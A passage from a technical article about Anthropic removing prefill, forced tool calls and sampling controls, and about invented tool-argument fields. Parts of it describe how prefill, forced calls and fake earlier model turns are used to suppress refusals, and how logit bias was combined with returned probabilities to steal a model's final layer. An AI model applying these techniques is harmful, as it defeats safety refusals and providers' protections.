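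Continuing an interrupted answer is harder too. Anthropic suggests quoting the end of the answer in a new user message and asking the model to carry on from there. A prefill let the model continue directly from the last token, but a model given a quotation may repeat a few words or start a new sentence, so a program that joins the two parts has to handle both cases.

Removing prefill also affected people who never meant to use it. Some users of Agno, a framework for building agents, had conversations that ended with a message from the model, which the API treats as a prefill. According to Agno's *Run Claude 4.6+ reliably across Anthropic, Bedrock, Vertex AI, and LiteLLM* (2026), these requests failed silently or came out malformed. Agno now adds a user message to the end of such conversations, which keeps the application running but means the model responds to a message that no user wrote.

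### Invented argument fields

When the model does call a tool, it can still get the arguments wrong, as Opus 4.8 did in the long coding session that Ronacher described in July. Sonnet 5 made the same mistake.

The session used Pi, a coding agent whose editing tool accepts a list of edits, each with two fields called `oldText` and `newText`. In the invalid calls, the model added at least one extra field to an edit. Ronacher saw `requireUnique`, `matchCase`, `in_file`, `notes`, `cost` and many other names. The extra fields came at the end of an edit, after a long string of replacement text, where the model must generate either a closing brace to end the edit or a comma to start another field.

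Ronacher guesses that the model adds extra fields because it was trained on a different editing tool. The one in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, takes an old string, a new string and one optional setting. A model trained heavily on that tool may have learned that an edit can have an extra field but have no name for it in Pi's version, so it makes up a plausible one each time. This fits the variety of names, but confirming it would require access to Anthropic's training. OpenAI's Codex models didn't have the problem in his tests, although he couldn't test the newest one.

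Forced tool choice wouldn't have prevented the extra field, because it fixes only the beginning of the call. Strict tool use did prevent it, because the mask allows only the closing brace at the point where the model would have added the field. Anthropic's first replacement therefore needs the `strict` setting. Without it, a developer who named the tool in the prompt would be relying on the model both to make the call and to get its fields right.

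If 20% of calls fail, as in that session, and failures are independent, 50 successful edits take an average of 62.5 attempts (50 / 0.8). The developer pays for the full replacement text in each failed attempt. Removing earlier thinking from the conversation halved the failure rate in Ronacher's tests, but the agent then has to work without that reasoning.

A request can include at most 20 strict tools. According to the Sonnet 5.5 guide, strict mode also isn't available for tool sets loaded through the Model Context Protocol or for those that operate a computer or browser. The restriction on customers with their own encryption keys still applies on Fable 5.2, but not on Opus 5.5. Claude Code doesn't use strict mode, probably because of the mode's limits on complexity, according to Ronacher. It discards unknown fields instead.

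Discarding unknown fields keeps calls working but can change what they do. If the model adds `"requireUnique": true` so that an edit applies only if the text occurs once, a program that drops the field may make the edit even when the text occurs several times. Keeping unknown fields is worse for security. If the model invents a free-text `notes` field and the program passes the whole object to another service, the field could carry private data with it. Rejecting the call avoids both problems, but the model then has to make the call again.

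### What the developer still controls

Developers still write the schemas for every model in the table, so they decide what the mask allows. Neither EnumAttack nor DictAttack needs the withdrawn controls.

With structured outputs, the replacement that go/chat adopted, the mask prevents the model from opening with "Sorry", just as the forced call did. The model can now think before it answers, which should help, but no published measurements compare how often Claude refuses harmful requests under a schema and under a forced call.

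A developer can still write earlier turns of the conversation, including ones attributed to the model. The only requirement in the API's error message for a prefill is that the conversation end with a user message. An invented answer earlier in the history can influence the model, as Liu and colleagues' attack showed, but the model then begins a new turn, in which it can disown that answer.

### Required calls at OpenAI and Google

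OpenAI and Google have offered similar settings. The table uses the names in their 2025 documentation.

| What the model must do | Anthropic | OpenAI | Google's Gemini API |
|---|---|---|---|
| Decide for itself | `auto` | `auto` | `AUTO` |
| Call at least one tool | `any`, on some models | `required` | `ANY` |
| Call one named tool | `tool`, on some models | The function's name | `ANY`, limited to that function |
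| Call no tool | `none` | `none` | `NONE` |

An application that supports several providers now has to treat Claude's newest models differently. LiteLLM translates OpenAI's `required` into Anthropic's `any`, so the same request that worked on Fable 5 fails on Fable 5.1.

A provider can require a tool call without using a prefill. The server could let the model think first, then apply a mask that allows only the opening of a tool call. This would keep both the reasoning and the guarantee of a call, but a model that decided to refuse while thinking still couldn't. To fix that, the provider would have to let the model refuse instead of making the call, which would give up the guarantee only when the model refuses.

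### Limits on logit bias after 2024

Security concerns had already led providers to restrict one way of controlling a model's output. OpenAI's API let developers make any token more or less likely through a setting called logit bias, which adds a number to the token's logit. The API could also return the log probabilities of the five most likely tokens. Each feature was useful and fairly harmless by itself.

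Together they let an outsider read the score of any token. Suppose a developer adds a large bias *B* to token *i*, so that it appears among the top five along with the model's usual first choice, *r*. The sum in the softmax is the same for both tokens and cancels out, which leaves:

log p_i − log p_r = (z_i + B) − z_r

Here z is a token's original logit. The developer knows *B* and can subtract it to get the difference between the two original logits. One request can do this for four tokens, so a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens takes about 25,000 requests.

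Nicholas Carlini and colleagues used this in *Stealing Part of a Production Language Model* (2024). A model computes its logits by multiplying a much shorter list of *d* internal numbers by a fixed matrix, its final layer. At most *d* of the resulting lists of logits can be linearly independent, however many prompts an attacker tries. An attacker who collects enough lists can therefore find *d* by counting the independent ones, and can use the lists to work out the matrix, up to a change of coordinates. For under $20, the researchers recovered the final layers of two small OpenAI models, ada and babbage, for which *d* was 1,024 and 2,048 respectively.

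OpenAI and Google responded by changing their APIs so that developers could no longer combine the two features to read whatever scores they wanted. This also affected honest users. A company that sorted messages into 20 departments could no longer find the probability of every department, only of the few that the API returned. The paper also described slower attacks that needed no returned probabilities, so the restriction made extraction more expensive but did not rule it out.

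That was a narrower change than Anthropic's, because developers kept both features and lost only the ability to combine them. They also knew the reason for the restriction.

Anthropic has since withdrawn other sampling controls. Starting with Opus 4.7 in April 2026, its Opus models reject any non-default value for temperature and for two settings that limit the choice to the most likely tokens. Developers who had lowered the temperature to make answers more consistent now have to rely on prompting. Anthropic doesn't explain this change in the release notes either. According to the notes, Sonnet 4.6 still accepts these settings, but text generated with non-default values may lack Anthropic's watermark, a statistical mark that identifies text as AI-generated. Fixed sampling settings may therefore make the watermark more reliable, though that may not be why Anthropic restricted them.
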